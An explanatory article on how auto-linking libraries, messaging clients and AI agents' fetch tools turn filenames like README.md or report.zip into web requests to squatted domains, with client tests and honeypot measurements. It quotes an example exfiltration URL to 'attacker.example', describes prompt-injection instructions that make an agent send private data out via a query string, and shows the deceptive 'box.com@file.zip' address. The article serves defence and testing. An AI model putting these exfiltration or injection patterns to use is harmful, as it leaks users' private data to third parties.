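# When AI agents turn text into links and fetch them: misread filenames, squatted domains and approval before fetching

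## How a piece of text becomes a web request

A web address, or URL (uniform resource locator), is a string that identifies something on the internet and how to request it. Chat programs, email clients and document viewers scan text for strings that look like addresses and turn them into clickable links. This is called auto-linking. AI agents can also request an address themselves, without anyone clicking a link.

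Problems start when the text was not meant as an address. `README.md` is the usual name for the file that introduces a software project, but it is also a valid domain name under .md, Moldova's top-level domain. A program given only the string cannot determine which one the writer meant. In *Automatic link creation for non-tld*, a thread on the support forum of the discussion software Discourse, a user complained that he had typed `README.md` as a filename and got a link. A reply pointed out that the domain existed and resolved.

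A name collision occurs when one string is both a valid filename and a valid domain name. Misrouting occurs when such a string leads to a request to a host, although the writer meant only a file or a different host. *Unpacking .zip* (2026), the first empirical study of this confusion, points out that most file systems permit every character that a domain name may contain and allow names of about the same length. Every domain name is therefore also a possible filename, and only context shows which one the writer meant.

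### The parts of an address

Berners-Lee (2005), in *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*, the internet standard for the syntax of addresses, divides an address into components with fixed punctuation between them. A made-up example from OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) contains the four that matter most here:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

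- The scheme, `https`, states how to make the request.
- The host, `attacker.example`, identifies the machine that is to receive it, usually by a domain name.
- The path, `/collect`, identifies a resource on that host.
- The query, which is everything after the question mark, passes further data to the host.

Whoever writes an address can freely choose its path and query, so the address can carry information outwards as well as identify a location. `http://README.md` has only a scheme and a host, with an empty path and no query. Hosts are case-insensitive, so `README.md` and `readme.md` are the same domain.

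The standard also allows user information, such as a login name, before the host, followed by an @ sign. In `https://box.com@file.zip`, the host is therefore `file.zip`, and `box.com` is only a supposed user name. Berners-Lee recommends that programs display the user information differently from the rest of the address, because someone may have written it to resemble a trusted domain.

### Who runs a top-level domain, and who can register a name

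A domain name is an ordered list of labels, normally written with dots between them. The last label is the top-level domain (TLD), such as .com or .md. *DNS Terminology* (Hoffman and Fujiwara, 2024) describes a TLD as a zone one layer below the root of the domain name system (DNS), and adds that TLDs have no special status in the DNS itself. Policy determines which TLDs are country-code and which are generic, and who may have a name.

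A community that meets under the Internet Corporation for Assigned Names and Numbers (ICANN) sets policy for the root. The Internet Assigned Numbers Authority (IANA) administers it, and according to IANA's *Report on Redelegation of the .md Top-Level Domain* (2003), this includes receiving and investigating requests to run or transfer a TLD. The organisation that runs a TLD is called its registry, and each registry sets its own conditions for registering names. Anyone can register a .com name. However, according to Eric Lawrence's blog post *New TLDs* (text/plain, 2023), an applicant for a .ie name has to prove a tie to Ireland, and an applicant for a .bank name needs an active banking licence.

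Moldova's TLD, .md, is at the open end of this range. IANA's record dates its creation to 24 March 1994 and lists a Moldovan public body, the Information Technology and Cyber Security Service, as the organisation in charge. The agency's *Frequently Asked Questions* page states that any person or company, resident in any country, may register a name, first come, first served. The fee is 450 lei a year, roughly 25 US dollars. The registry treats an application as the applicant's warranty that they are entitled to the name. It updates the zone every two hours, so a new name can be in use on the day of purchase.

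These terms may change. Fomin reports in *ARCOM unveils new regulations for managing Moldova’s .md domain* that Moldova's communications regulator sought comment from 19 May to 17 June 2026 on draft rules that add mechanisms against the misuse of domain names.

A .md registration also lasts only one to three years, and once the registry deletes a name, anyone can apply for it. Berners-Lee's standard warns that a domain may change hands for reasons the writer of an address did not foresee. A link that was harmless when written can therefore later lead to a site run by someone else.

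### Endings that are also file extensions

Top-level domains have overlapped with file extensions since the first public ones were announced in 1984. Those included .com, which was already the extension for executable programs on the operating systems CP/M and DOS. Paraguay's .py, also the extension for Python programs, and Saint Helena's .sh, also the extension for shell scripts, have been in use since the 1990s.

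Google revived the worry when it decided to sell names under .zip and .mov, which are also the file extensions of compressed archives and videos. It had become the registry for both in 2014 but at first kept them closed to the public. According to Google Registry's *Launch details for eight new TLDs* (2023), trademark holders could register names from 2 April 2023, anyone willing to pay an extra fee from 3 May, and everyone else from 10 May. The company's public announcement, *8 new top-level domains for dads, grads and techies* (Yeh, 2023), presented .zip as a domain for short, trackable links.

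Security researchers objected that messaging platforms might now turn ordinary filenames into links to strangers' sites. Google replied, according to CircleID, that confusion between file and domain names was not new and that browsers had protections in place. The confusion is not new, since .com is also a file extension. But this does little to answer the objection, because almost everyone now reads a string ending in .com as an address, whereas they usually still read one ending in .zip or .md as a file.

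*Unpacking .zip* identifies eleven TLDs that are popular as file extensions but little used as domains: .do, .download, .java, .md, .mov, .properties, .pub, .py, .run, .sb and .zip. It measures popularity by user ratings in a catalogue of file formats, and counts a TLD as little used if fewer than 100,000 of its names appear in three months of public records of website certificates. ICANN closed a new application round for generic TLDs on 12 August 2026 with more than 1,600 primary applications, according to CADE's *ICANN receives more than 1,600 applications in 2026 new gTLD round*. Any approved TLD that is also a file extension would create new collisions.

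### Lookup, request and answer

Before a program can contact a host, it needs the host's numerical internet address. To get it, the program sends the host's name to a resolver, a server often run by an internet provider or a company. If the resolver has no recent answer in its cache, it works down the hierarchy of name servers. For `readme.md`, the root servers identify the servers for .md, which identify the servers responsible for `readme.md`, and these return the address.

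If the name does not exist, the lookup returns an error code called NXDOMAIN. These errors can help show which filenames are leaking into the DNS, because a lookup for an unregistered .zip name is more likely to come from a misread filename than from a visit to a website. The inference is imperfect, since *Unpacking .zip* notes that NXDOMAIN sometimes means that a domain is unavailable for some other reason. A name with no website also does not necessarily return NXDOMAIN. It may exist but have no record of the type requested, a result that Hoffman and Fujiwara list separately as NODATA. A tester checking whether a name is free to register should not treat the two results as the same.

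When the lookup succeeds, the program connects to the server and sends a request in HTTP, the protocol of the web. The request contains the path and the query, and usually a header that identifies the requesting software. The `https` scheme adds encryption, which hides the path and query from others on the network but not from the server. OpenAI notes that websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request. The server then sends back whatever its owner has chosen to put there.

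### Agents that fetch

An AI agent is a program that lets a language model take actions through tools. One of the simplest is a fetch tool. The model writes an address, and the software around the model requests that address and adds the returned text to what the model reads next. Some agents operate a whole browser. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an agent that views pages, clicks and types inside the user's own browser, with the same context and data as the user.

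From here on, "fetch" means any automatic request by an agent or its software for the content at an address, whether or not the user sees it happen. This includes requests sent to load an image embedded in a reply or to prepare a link preview.

The danger specific to agents is prompt injection, in which someone writes text to make an AI system that reads it act against its user's wishes. For example, a web page might contain an instruction to disregard earlier instructions and send the user's address to the page's author. A conventional browser would simply display that sentence, but a language model receives it as text, like everything else it works from, and may follow it. As a comment in Fortune (2025) put it, agentic browsers allow content "to shape behavior, not just be displayed".

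### One filename, followed through

Suppose an assistant has been helping somebody install a program.

1. The assistant writes "see README.md". So far this is plain text, and no program has requested anything.
2. The chat software recognises .md as a real TLD, adds `http://` in front of the filename and displays a link. (How linking software makes this decision is the subject of the next section.) An agent that reads the same sentence may skip the link and pass `http://README.md` straight to its fetch tool.
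3. Something sets off a request. A person clicks, or a messaging service prepares a preview, or the agent calls its tool.
4. The requesting program looks up `readme.md`. Unless a resolver has a cached answer, the query reaches the servers for Moldova's .md. Had nobody registered the name, NXDOMAIN would end the sequence here, but the filename would already have left the conversation.
5. The name exists, so the lookup returns a numerical address, and the program sends that server an HTTP request for its front page.
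6. The server answers. A browser shows the answer to a person, or the agent's software hands it to the model, which was expecting installation instructions and has no particular reason to think it received anything else.

Every program in this sequence can work as intended. The only mistake is in step 2, where software picked one reading of ambiguous text without the information to know which was right.

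### Three harms

A DNS query reveals the hostname, and an HTTP request adds the path, the query string and the sender's network address. Revealing `README.md` matters little because many software projects have a file with that name. A filename that mentions a customer or an unannounced merger would reveal more. The serious case is URL exfiltration, in which an attacker gets a model to put private data in the URL, as in OpenAI's `attacker.example` illustration. This attack doesn't require a misread filename, but the data leaves the same way, through an automatic request to a host that someone else controls.

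**A person is misled.** Someone who clicks on `report.zip` expects an archive and may accept a download or a login page from whoever owns that domain. This is easier because many office workers are used to clickable filenames that open web pages. Microsoft Outlook, for example, has introduced links that hide the host and show only the name of a cloud document. CircleID thought criminals were unlikely to register large numbers of domains to catch a few victims, but added that one employee who installs malware can endanger a company's whole network.

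**An agent takes in hostile content.** The threat model in *Unpacking .zip* covers information leaks, unwanted downloads, attacks on browsers and the deception of people. Agents add the risk of prompt injection, and the damage depends on what else the agent can do. An agent that can only summarise pages may produce a false summary. One that can also read the user's mail may obey an injected instruction to fetch a second address with the contents of a message in the query, which leaks the message. A defence against one of these harms may not prevent another. For example, OpenAI says that its safeguard against leaks through addresses does not guarantee that a page's content is trustworthy.

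### Who can profit

*Unpacking .zip* distinguishes three kinds of adversary, and they need very different amounts of effort.

Some parties can see mistaken lookups just by watching DNS traffic. A TLD's registry, such as Google for .zip or Moldova's registry for .md, can see most mistaken lookups under that TLD, including those for unregistered names, except when they are answered from caches. A resolver's operator also sees its own users' lookups. These observers see the domain name but not the URL's path or query string, and watching alone doesn't let them serve their own page in response.

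A squatted domain is one that someone buys to receive traffic meant for something else. Its owner can see lookups for the domain and its subdomains, read the requests that follow, and decide what to send back. Some of this traffic comes from misread filenames, and some comes from plausible domain names that language models invent, which a later section covers.

The remaining group plants text in messages, posts or web pages so that software misreads part of it or a person clicks the wrong link. The `box.com@file.zip` address is an example. Planting works best when combined with registering a domain, because someone has to own the domain the link leads to. When the target is a person, the text must also persuade them to click. If an agent fetches addresses on its own, no one has to click, and a string in a document it reads may be enough.

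## Finding where software turns filenames into links

In the example above, `README.md` became a web address when the chat software put `http://` in front of it. A small library usually does this, after searching the text for anything resembling an address. Products use different libraries and settings, so the same filename can be plain text in one program and a link in another. Agent developers have to find every such library between the model and the reader, including the one in the messaging service that carries the reply.

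### How a linking program decides

An example in the documentation for *linkify-it*, markdown-it's widely used linking library, shows how the software decides whether to turn text into a link. It processes the input `Site github.com!` in four steps.

1. It finds a dotted string that could be a host. Here that is `github.com`, without the exclamation mark.
2. It compares the ending, .com, with a list of TLDs that it accepts.
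3. It adds a scheme, because the text has none, and gets `http://github.com`.
4. It emits a link that still reads `github.com` on the screen but leads to the full address.

`README.md` passes through the same steps if .md is on the list. None of the steps use the surrounding words, so "open README.md in your editor" and "visit README.md" produce the same link. The library doesn't look the name up in the DNS either, so it will link a name nobody has registered.

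Linking libraries differ mainly in the second step. Some accept a bare name with a known ending, and others ignore bare names altogether.

### A permissive rule: linkify-it

markdown-it is a program that converts Markdown into web pages. Markdown is the plain-text notation for headings, lists and links in which language models usually format their replies. A developer who wants markdown-it to link plain addresses has to switch this on with the option `linkify: true`, which, according to markdown-it, hands the work to linkify-it.

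linkify-it has a setting of its own for names without a scheme, `fuzzyLink`, and this one is on by default. A developer who turns on linking in order to catch `https://` addresses therefore also gets links for bare names. By default, the documentation from markdown-it shows, the library accepts these endings on a bare name:

- any two-letter TLD, which means the country codes
- sixteen longer endings, which in alphabetical order are .aero, .asia, .biz, .com, .coop, .edu, .gov, .info, .museum, .name, .net, .org, .pro, .shop, .web and .xxx, and also the Cyrillic .рф
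- TLDs in their encoded form, which begins with `xn--` and represents endings in other scripts.

These defaults reach a lot of software. Socket's package record *linkify-it*, last updated on 1 July 2026, shows about 27 million downloads a week. That figure includes repeated installations by the same developers, so it doesn't measure how many products link bare names. linkify-it-py, a Python version, documents the same default endings, so an agent written in Python can pick them up too.

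### A strict rule: GitHub Flavored Markdown

The *Autolinks (extension)* section of GitHub's Markdown specification sets a stricter condition. A plain string becomes a link only if it begins with `www.` or a scheme such as `https://`. It must also be at the start of a line or come after a space, `*`, `_`, `~` or `(`.

The specification requires a "valid domain" after the `www.` or the scheme, but defines one only by its characters, without a list of TLDs. A valid domain consists of letters, digits, underscores, hyphens and full stops, with at least one full stop and no underscore in the last two segments.

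Two independent imitations of GitHub's rule confirm this reading. The Markdown package for the programming language Dart uses a search pattern that matches only strings starting with `http://`, `https://`, `ftp://` or `www.`. py-gfm's *gfm.autolink*, an extension for Python, started from a more permissive pattern by John Gruber that would accept `foo.com/bar`. Its developers changed the pattern after finding that GitHub did not turn such strings into links.

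### Five file endings through both rules

To apply linkify-it's rule, a tester needs to know which endings are real TLDs. IANA's official list, *Top-Level Domains*, shows .md, .py, .sh and .zip as active. It has no entry for .go, the extension for Go programs.

The table applies the two documented rules to one filename for each ending, and then to two variants with something in front.

| String | Who has the ending | linkify-it, default settings | GitHub's rule |
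|---|---|---|---|
| `README.md` | Moldova | link | plain text |
| `setup.py` | Paraguay | link | plain text |
| `install.sh` | Saint Helena | link | plain text |
| `report.zip` | Google's registry company | plain text | plain text |
| `main.go` | nobody | plain text | plain text |
| `http://report.zip` | Google's registry company | link | link |
| `www.main.go` | nobody | plain text | link |

As the .zip row shows, linkify-it does not link .zip filenames by default, even though .zip caused most of the public worry. The library accepts every country-code TLD but only a short list of generic ones, which omits .zip. If a developer loads a complete list of TLDs, `report.zip` and `clip.mov` also become links. The first usage example in the library's documentation loads such a list, so a developer who copies it gets the wider behaviour, perhaps without having thought about filenames.

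The country-code default turns many programmers' filenames into links because their extensions are also country codes. Besides .md, .py and .sh, IANA's list has .rs (Serbia, and Rust programs), .pl (Poland, and Perl), .so (Somalia, and shared libraries on Linux) and .ml (Mali, and OCaml). JavaScript filenames are not linked because no country has the code .js. A release of linkify-it in April 2015 tightened the check on two-letter endings to stop it from linking `node.js`.

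The last row shows a weakness of the strict rule. GitHub's specification has no list of TLDs, so `www.main.go` qualifies as a link although no such domain can exist at present. This matters little for filenames, which rarely begin with `www.`. "Strict" therefore describes what must come before the name, not how carefully the software checks the name.

The user who complained about `README.md` in *Automatic link creation for non-tld* liked getting automatic links for `google.com` and `gimp.org`, and GitHub's strict rule would remove those links too.

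### The same library in different products

Products that use the same library can link different text, because developers change the defaults. Discourse has a site setting that controls which endings turn text into a link. A participant in *Automatic link creation for non-tld* identified it as "markdown linkify tlds". Two Discourse forums can therefore treat the same filename differently.

Signal's desktop messaging app also uses linkify-it. A code change titled *Only fuzzy linkify TLDs in place in 2010* replaced the library's default endings with twenty generic TLDs that already existed in 2010, from .aero to .travel. This list excludes .zip and all country codes, so with it `README.md` and `setup.py` stay plain text. `https://README.md` still becomes a link because the restriction covers only bare names.

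The publishing platform Ghost went further in the preview pane of its Markdown editor. *Disable fuzzy auto-linking of URLs in markdown preview* sets `fuzzyLink` to false, so the pane links only text that begins with a scheme. When a user of the note-taking program Joplin complained that an address no longer became a link, a reply in *Link auto-generation issue* explained that Joplin now seemed to require a scheme too, because it had been linking names such as `file.py` and `file.pl`.

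All of these developers ran into the problem in ordinary use and solved it in different ways. An agent builder can therefore learn from documentation what to expect from a library, but can find out what the finished product does with a filename only by testing it.

### What seven messaging and email clients did

*Unpacking .zip* reports tests of this kind on finished products. The researchers tested WhatsApp, Telegram, Snapchat, Instagram, Messenger, Gmail and Outlook, mostly on an iPad, and gave each client up to five sets of strings.

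In the first tests, all seven clients linked ordinary names under endings such as .com and .org, but none linked names under .lx, .lss or .rfl, which don't exist as TLDs. Every client therefore checks endings against some list rather than just looking for a dot.

To test file endings, the researchers typed names ending in .zip, .download, .mov, .properties, .app, .info, .pub, .py and .md. Of the three .zip names, `document.zip` was registered and led to a server, `something.zip` was registered but had no server address, and `somethinggg.zip` was unregistered. They counted a client as safe if it neither linked nor previewed a name.

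Telegram linked every name in this test. WhatsApp, Snapchat, Instagram and Outlook linked only names ending in .info, and Gmail only those ending in .info and .app. Messenger linked none of the file endings, but it generated link previews for names ending in .py and .md. The researchers considered this a risk in itself, because a preview card beneath a filename can look like an attached file.

Some clients did not link .zip, and the researchers concluded that their developers had deliberately excluded certain file endings, each in their own way. To check whether these clients were using old lists that lack recent TLDs, the researchers tested them with endings of various ages, including .biz from 2001, .xyz from 2014 and .dog from 2015. Age did not explain the results. None of these clients linked .py, which dates from 1991 and is older than most of the endings in the test.

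This conclusion is an inference from the clients' behaviour, not their code, and the tests cover only a few devices and versions. But the tests show that an agent's builder can't assume clients follow a common standard. If an agent sends `README.md` as plain text to one user on WhatsApp and another on Telegram, the WhatsApp user sees a filename and the Telegram user sees a link to a stranger's website.

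### When the link and the preview disagree

Messenger's previews for unlinked .py and .md names suggest that separate parts of the product decide what to link and what to preview. A further test in *Unpacking .zip* showed this split more clearly. The researchers sent the deceptive address from the previous section, `https://box.com@file.zip`, whose real host is `file.zip`.

Messenger and Instagram correctly linked to `file.zip` but showed a preview of `box.com`. A reader would have seen the title and picture of a well-known storage service above a link to somebody else's server. The fault occurred with any TLD, not just .zip. The researchers think the app created the link while Meta's servers prepared the preview with a different parser, the code that divides an address into its parts. Meta fixed the fault after the researchers reported it.

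Without the `https://`, `box.com@file.zip` looks like an email address. WhatsApp, Snapchat, Messenger, Outlook, and Telegram on the iPad and iPhone treated it as one. Gmail left it as plain text. Telegram on a Mac switched to a browser other than the user's default, and the researchers could not explain why.

Agents can have the same fault wherever two components parse the same address separately. If a safety check extracts `box.com` from the address and the fetch tool then contacts `file.zip`, the check has approved the wrong host. Builders can avoid this by parsing the address once and passing the resulting host to every later step.

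### One message, two linking programs

An agent's reply often passes through more than one program that can turn text into links. The agent's own software may convert the model's Markdown for display, and a messaging service then processes the result. Whether a filename ends up as a link depends on its form when it reaches the messaging service.

If the model writes "See README.md" and the agent's software passes this on unchanged, whether the filename becomes a link depends only on the service's rule. Telegram turns it into a link, but WhatsApp and GitHub do not.

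If the agent's software first runs the text through linkify-it with its default settings and then sends the service the link's full address, the service receives `http://README.md`. GitHub's rule would have ignored the bare filename, but it accepts this string because it has a scheme. Signal's restricted version of linkify-it also accepts it, because its list of endings applies only to bare names. Both rely on the missing scheme to recognize a bare name, and the first program has already added one.

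The added scheme can also cause a fetch that would not otherwise happen. According to *Unpacking .zip*, Telegram prepares a preview only if the string begins with `http://` or `https://` or ends with a slash. The study also reports previews for .info names in its file-ending test without mentioning either condition, so testers should try each form separately. If Telegram does apply these conditions, a bare `README.md` leads to a request only when a person clicks it, whereas `http://README.md` can lead to one as soon as the agent sends the message.

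One permissive program anywhere in the chain is enough to turn a filename into a link, even if the others are strict. A builder who fixes only the agent's own display code may therefore see correct output on the test screen while users of a messaging service still get links. A patch to the agent program OpenClaw, described in a later section, deals with filenames on their way to such a service.

### Three places where an agent can be caught

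In all the cases so far, an agent sends out text containing a filename, and downstream software turns the filename into a link. The model has made no error, and it usually can't detect the link because the software adds it after the text is sent.

An agent can also receive a filename that is already a link. Its software often converts forum pages, emails and chat histories into text and keeps the link addresses. If a forum had turned `README.md` into a link, the model may receive the Markdown link `[README.md](http://README.md)`. The original writer typed only a filename, but the model receives an explicit address and may fetch it to find the installation instructions.

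At this point it is hard to tell what the writer meant. When linkify-it makes a match, it leaves the `schema` field empty if the text had no scheme of its own, but the finished link contains `http://README.md` either way. The remaining suspicious pattern is a label that looks like a filename and an address that is the same name with `http://` in front and no path. A genuine link to the website `readme.md` could look the same, so this pattern justifies a closer look but doesn't prove a mistake.

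The last place to check is the fetch tool itself. A model trying to read a local file might call the web tool by mistake and pass it `README.md`. If the tool requires a complete address, it returns an error, and the model can try again with the right tool. But if the tool adds the missing `https://`, it sends a request to an address under `.md`, Moldova's country domain.

Such a tool may have no list of TLDs, so it would also try to fetch `main.go`, which both linking rules in the table leave as plain text. The lookup would fail because .go doesn't exist, but the DNS query might already have revealed the filename.

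The evidence for these three places is uneven. The client tests and the forum complaints document the linking of outgoing text, but *Unpacking .zip* provides no evidence about the other two places. Its researchers tested software that people use to write to one another. When they later analysed traffic to their own domains, they removed requests from OpenAI's crawler GPTBot and from common programming tools such as curl and python-requests, which were irrelevant to their question. An agent's fetch tool may well identify itself as one of these, so its requests would have been removed too. Although the study did not observe an agent making the error, incoming links and fetch tools are worth testing because the components described here can produce it.

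### A test for one's own product

A tester can check all three places in an afternoon with one registered domain. A .md domain is suitable because anyone can buy one. The procedure below uses `yourname.md` as a placeholder.

1. Set up a server for `yourname.md` and all its subdomains, and log every DNS lookup and web request. Names such as `a1.yourname.md` and `a2.yourname.md` are valid filenames as well as hosts under the tester's control. Using a different one at each stage shows which stage caused a request.
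2. Write a test message. Include `a1.yourname.md`, and long nonsense names under .py, .sh, .zip and .go that nobody has registered. Add `https://example.com`, which should become a link, and a name ending in .lx, which should not. Unregistered names can reveal linking but not previews, because there is no page to fetch.
3. Have the agent send the message through every channel the product supports. At each stage, save the text that goes in and the text that comes out, and search for an `http://` that the model did not write. Then check what the recipient sees.
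4. Repeat with `a2.yourname.md/`, `http://a3.yourname.md` and `https://example.com@a4.yourname.md`. For the last of these, compare the host in the preview with the host that the link opens. They should be the same.
5. Put `a5.yourname.md` as plain text in a forum post, an email and a document that the agent can read. Log exactly what the model receives, and look for a link that was not in the original.
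6. Call the fetch tool directly, without the model, and give it `a6.yourname.md` and a nonsense name ending in .go. The tool should reject both. A request in the server's log means that it added a scheme to the first. For the .go name, check the local DNS log, since no outside server can receive the request.

A preview request in the log may come from the messaging service's servers and not the user's device, so searching only for familiar network addresses could miss it. The User-Agent header, in which software identifies itself, often helps. In the study's tests, Telegram's preview requests used the name TelegramBot and Instagram's used facebookexternalhit, while Messenger's used WhatsApp. Anyone can forge this header, but there is little reason to suspect forgery in a private test with a fresh subdomain.

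The results hold only for the versions and devices tested. Telegram behaved differently on a Mac than on an iPad, and Meta changed the behaviour of two products after a single report. The test message is therefore worth keeping and reusing whenever the product adds a channel, updates its Markdown library or replaces its fetch tool.

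## Measuring how often misread filenames reach a domain

A test message shows whether one product misreads a filename, but not how often this happens in ordinary use. Internet providers can help measure the frequency by counting lookups for filenames that nobody has registered as domains, and owners of domains that look like filenames can help by logging the requests they receive. *Unpacking .zip* used both methods.

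Neither method gives a rate, because the study has no figure for how many times people and programs wrote `gitlab.zip`. It counts only the mistakes that reached the DNS or a server.

### Failed lookups at one internet provider

The researchers used anonymous daily totals of DNS responses from a large North American internet provider, covering January to October 2024. The totals show which names customers' machines looked up, but not which machines or programs looked them up. The researchers kept only the NXDOMAIN responses and picked out by hand the names that looked most like filenames.

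Among the examples, `gitlab.zip` had 331,810 failed lookups, or about 1,100 a day. `crowdstrike-hotfix.zip` had 7,709 and `downloaddataen.zip` had 3,128. `tvmt11-flex-ota-2023_04_14-10_19_39-signed.zip` had by far the most, with 15,923,035. It looks like the name of a firmware update, since "ota" is the usual abbreviation for "over-the-air" updates.

The firmware file accounts for 97.5 per cent of lookups for the study's seven listed names. People are unlikely to have typed such a name about 50,000 times a day. More likely, a line of devices treated the filename as a hostname and kept retrying, although anonymous totals can't confirm this. The study's largest number, 15.9 million lookups, may therefore reflect one faulty product and should not be read as a count of separate mistakes by people.

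Another example, `simcare-v1.1.zip`, had only 491 lookups but shows how a squatter could catch many filenames at once. The dot in its version number makes this filename a subdomain of `1.zip`, so whoever owns `1.zip` can receive the lookups for every filename that ends in `.1.zip`. Cisco Talos, Cisco's security research group, gives the example of a chat program that turned the filename `update.exe.zip` into a link. That name belongs to the owner of `exe.zip`. Likewise, under Moldova's `.md` domain, `notes.v2.md` belongs to the owner of `v2.md`. A squatter therefore only has to guess a common version number or double extension, not a whole filename.

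Talos also shows what a lookup can reveal even if no web request follows. From May 2023 it searched the data of Umbrella, Cisco's DNS filtering service, for .zip names and published several real filenames with parts hidden. One contained the version number of a VPN program, from which an attacker could learn that a company was running old software. Another contained the bank name HSBC, "equity orders" and a date, and others appeared to contain employee or user ID numbers. Talos warns that attackers could use such details to write convincing messages to a company's staff. It gives no totals, so these examples can't be used to estimate how often filenames leak.

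### Six domains that look like files

For the second measurement, the researchers set up a honeypot, a group of servers used only to attract and record traffic. They chose .zip from their eleven candidate endings partly because many names under .download carry premium prices, and .py and .sb restrict who may register.

The researchers registered six .zip domains. Two of them, `metadata.zip` and `manifest.zip`, are simple names that many local files might have. The other four came from the list of failed lookups: `gitlab.zip`, `crowdstrike-hotfix.zip`, `downloaddataen.zip` and a long firmware name beginning with `wallboard`. They also registered two control domains, `metadata.rodeo` and `manifest.observer`, whose endings are not file extensions.

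From February to September 2025, the six .zip domains received 328,376 web requests and the two control domains received 67,737. Any new domain attracts automated programs that look for weaknesses or build indexes. At the controls' average of about 34,000 requests each, six domains would have received about 203,000 even if no filename had been misread. The researchers therefore removed suspected automated traffic in five steps.

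| What the researchers removed | Requests left |
|---|---|
| Nothing yet | 328,376 |
| Networks that had also contacted a control domain | 187,665 |
| Requests for anything except the front page, the site icon and a few similar files | 57,140 |
| Requests whose User-Agent header named a known bot or programming tool | 44,623 |
| Networks that had sent such headers or had looked for passwords and configuration files | 31,567 |
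| Addresses that had sent more than four requests within one second | 29,379 |

A "network" in the table is a block of 256 neighbouring internet addresses. The researchers removed whole blocks because a scanner may use several addresses, but this also removed any ordinary users in those blocks. The second step relies on their tests of messaging apps, in which clicks and previews requested only the front page and a few icons. Scanners often requested other files, such as `/.git/credentials`, which might contain a password.

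About 9 per cent of the original requests remained after filtering. The true share caused by filename confusion could be higher or lower, because the filters can discard genuine mistakes and keep requests from careful scanners. They also discard requests from common programming tools, including any that came from an agent's fetch tool.

### Which requests came from a known client

The researchers had sent test messages through each client to learn what its requests look like. They compared the 29,379 remaining requests with these fingerprints, and 3,150 of them, or 10.7 per cent, matched.

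| Client | Previews | Clicks | Could the study recognise a click? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Telegram | 16 | 2,391 | On Android only |
| Messenger | 373 | 71 | Yes |
| Instagram | 244 | 34 | Yes |
| WhatsApp | 11 | 0 | No |
| Snapchat | 10 | 0 | On iPhone only |
| Outlook | none made | 0 | No |
| Gmail | none made | 0 | No |

The last column affects how to interpret the zeros. When someone taps a link in WhatsApp, the phone opens its usual browser and the request looks like any other visit from that browser, so WhatsApp's zero doesn't mean that nobody clicked. Telegram's count is high partly because it links more filenames than the other clients, as the previous section described, and partly because a header identifies the app on Android.

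The 2,391 Telegram requests probably represent far fewer visits, because a browser usually requests the page and then its icon. Of the addresses that sent click requests, 70.9 per cent made exactly two requests. Even if every request had been a separate click, the total for all clients would be about 12 a day across six domains. The requests don't show what people expected to find when they clicked.

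Some of the previews are doubtful. More than half of all preview requests came from Vietnam, mostly with headers naming Meta's apps, but the researchers found no evidence that Meta has servers there. They suspect that automated programs forged the headers. The smallest counts may also include the researchers' own test messages, which went to the same domains and aren't removed by any of the five filtering steps. The Telegram clicks are more convincing because they came from more than 200 networks and mostly from India, where Telegram has the most downloads.

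### The 26,229 requests without a known source

The remaining 26,229 requests matched none of the fingerprints. They could be clicks from apps that open an ordinary browser, or requests from scanners that passed the filters. The data therefore don't support the inference in the paper's introduction that this majority is a sign of widespread confusion between filenames and domains.

The control domains can't settle the question because the first filter removed every network that had contacted them, which left no control traffic for comparison. A better design would use one control domain to build the filter and a second to test it. If the second control still had thousands of requests after filtering, a similar number at a .zip domain would be weak evidence of misread filenames.

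Even that comparison would be imperfect, because companies watch for new domains that contain their brands. This monitoring could bring visits to a name such as `gitlab.zip` that an ordinary control such as `metadata.rodeo` would not get.

The researchers did find some partial explanations by reading other headers:

- 1,804 requests named Google's Android search app as their origin, and all were for `metadata.zip`. The researchers assume that people had typed a filename into the search box or that another app had passed it on. But these requests began on 1 August 2025 and all had the same User-Agent header, which would also fit an automated program.
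- 594 requests came from the browser built into the Chinese messaging app WeChat. Only five of them asked for the site's icon, and the researchers could not establish that they were previews.
- 85 requests came from Skype's preview service, on Microsoft's own network. This is the clearest of the three cases, because both the header and the network match.

If all of these belong to the unmatched group, about 23,700 requests remain unexplained. They justify further measurement but should not go into an estimate of how many filenames were misread.

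The researchers also say they lacked the data to determine whether anyone was exploiting the confusion. Their results for .zip may not apply to .md or .py, as people use those endings differently.

An agent's builder can measure the missing rate for their own product by counting the filenames in the agent's output and tool calls, then searching the DNS logs of the agent's machines for those names. Lookups by a recipient's phone or a messaging service will not appear in those logs, so the builder still needs a test domain to count them, as in the previous section.

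### What people did with .zip domains

Registration figures show who was ready to receive misrouted traffic or to deceive people with a domain name that looks like a filename, but they don't measure how much traffic arrived.

In mid-May 2023, two weeks after .zip opened to the public, *Phishing attacks already using the .zip TLD*, by the anti-fraud company Netcraft, reported fewer than 5,000 registered .zip domains. Netcraft had found phishing on five, all of them offline by then. One had imitated a Microsoft login page but carried the words "THIS IS FOR TESTING". About 200 names contained "installer" or "update", and 48 domains redirected visitors to the music video used in a well-known internet prank. At about the same time, a survey by SANS, a security training organisation, found that 1,506 of the 1,928 .zip domains it examined were parked, meaning that they had owners but showed only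 a default page, often one supplied by the company that sold the name.

By 19 June 2023 there were 13,796 .zip domains, according to the DNS Research Federation's *The .zip TLD* (2023). The organisation checked them against public lists of abusive domains and found 27 listed, 18 for spam, seven for phishing and two for malware. That rate, 0.20 per cent, was slightly below the organisation's 2022 figure of 0.22 per cent for all TLDs. New generic TLDs had averaged 0.34 per cent and European country-code TLDs 0.06 per cent. The organisation cautions that it had not rigorously tested its method.

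Six months after its first report, Netcraft's *zip TLD* (2023) counted 16,705 .zip domains and 56 that the company had blocked as malicious since the launch. Most of the blocked domains imitated Microsoft, Google or the games shop Steam. Among the serious attacks, `apecoin.zip` tricked visitors into handing over their cryptocurrency, and `v0464309.zip` offered a fake Chrome update that stole email passwords. Far more .zip sites warned visitors about the danger than carried out an attack, but Netcraft noted that criminals could copy the tricks these sites demonstrated.

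Criminals used .zip names as bait in these cases, but software may not have misread a filename, because a criminal can also send someone a complete link to `v0464309.zip`.

Later figures are harder to find. Cybercrime Information Center's *Phishing Activity*, which covers May 2025 to April 2026, ranks TLDs by phishing domains per 10,000 names, but includes only TLDs with at least 30,000 domains. If .zip were still the size Netcraft reported in 2023, it would be too small to appear. Google still sells .zip domains, and the examples on Google Registry's *zip* page include `YourAssets.zip` and `YourProject.zip`, which could also be the names of archives on somebody's computer.

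### The case for worrying less

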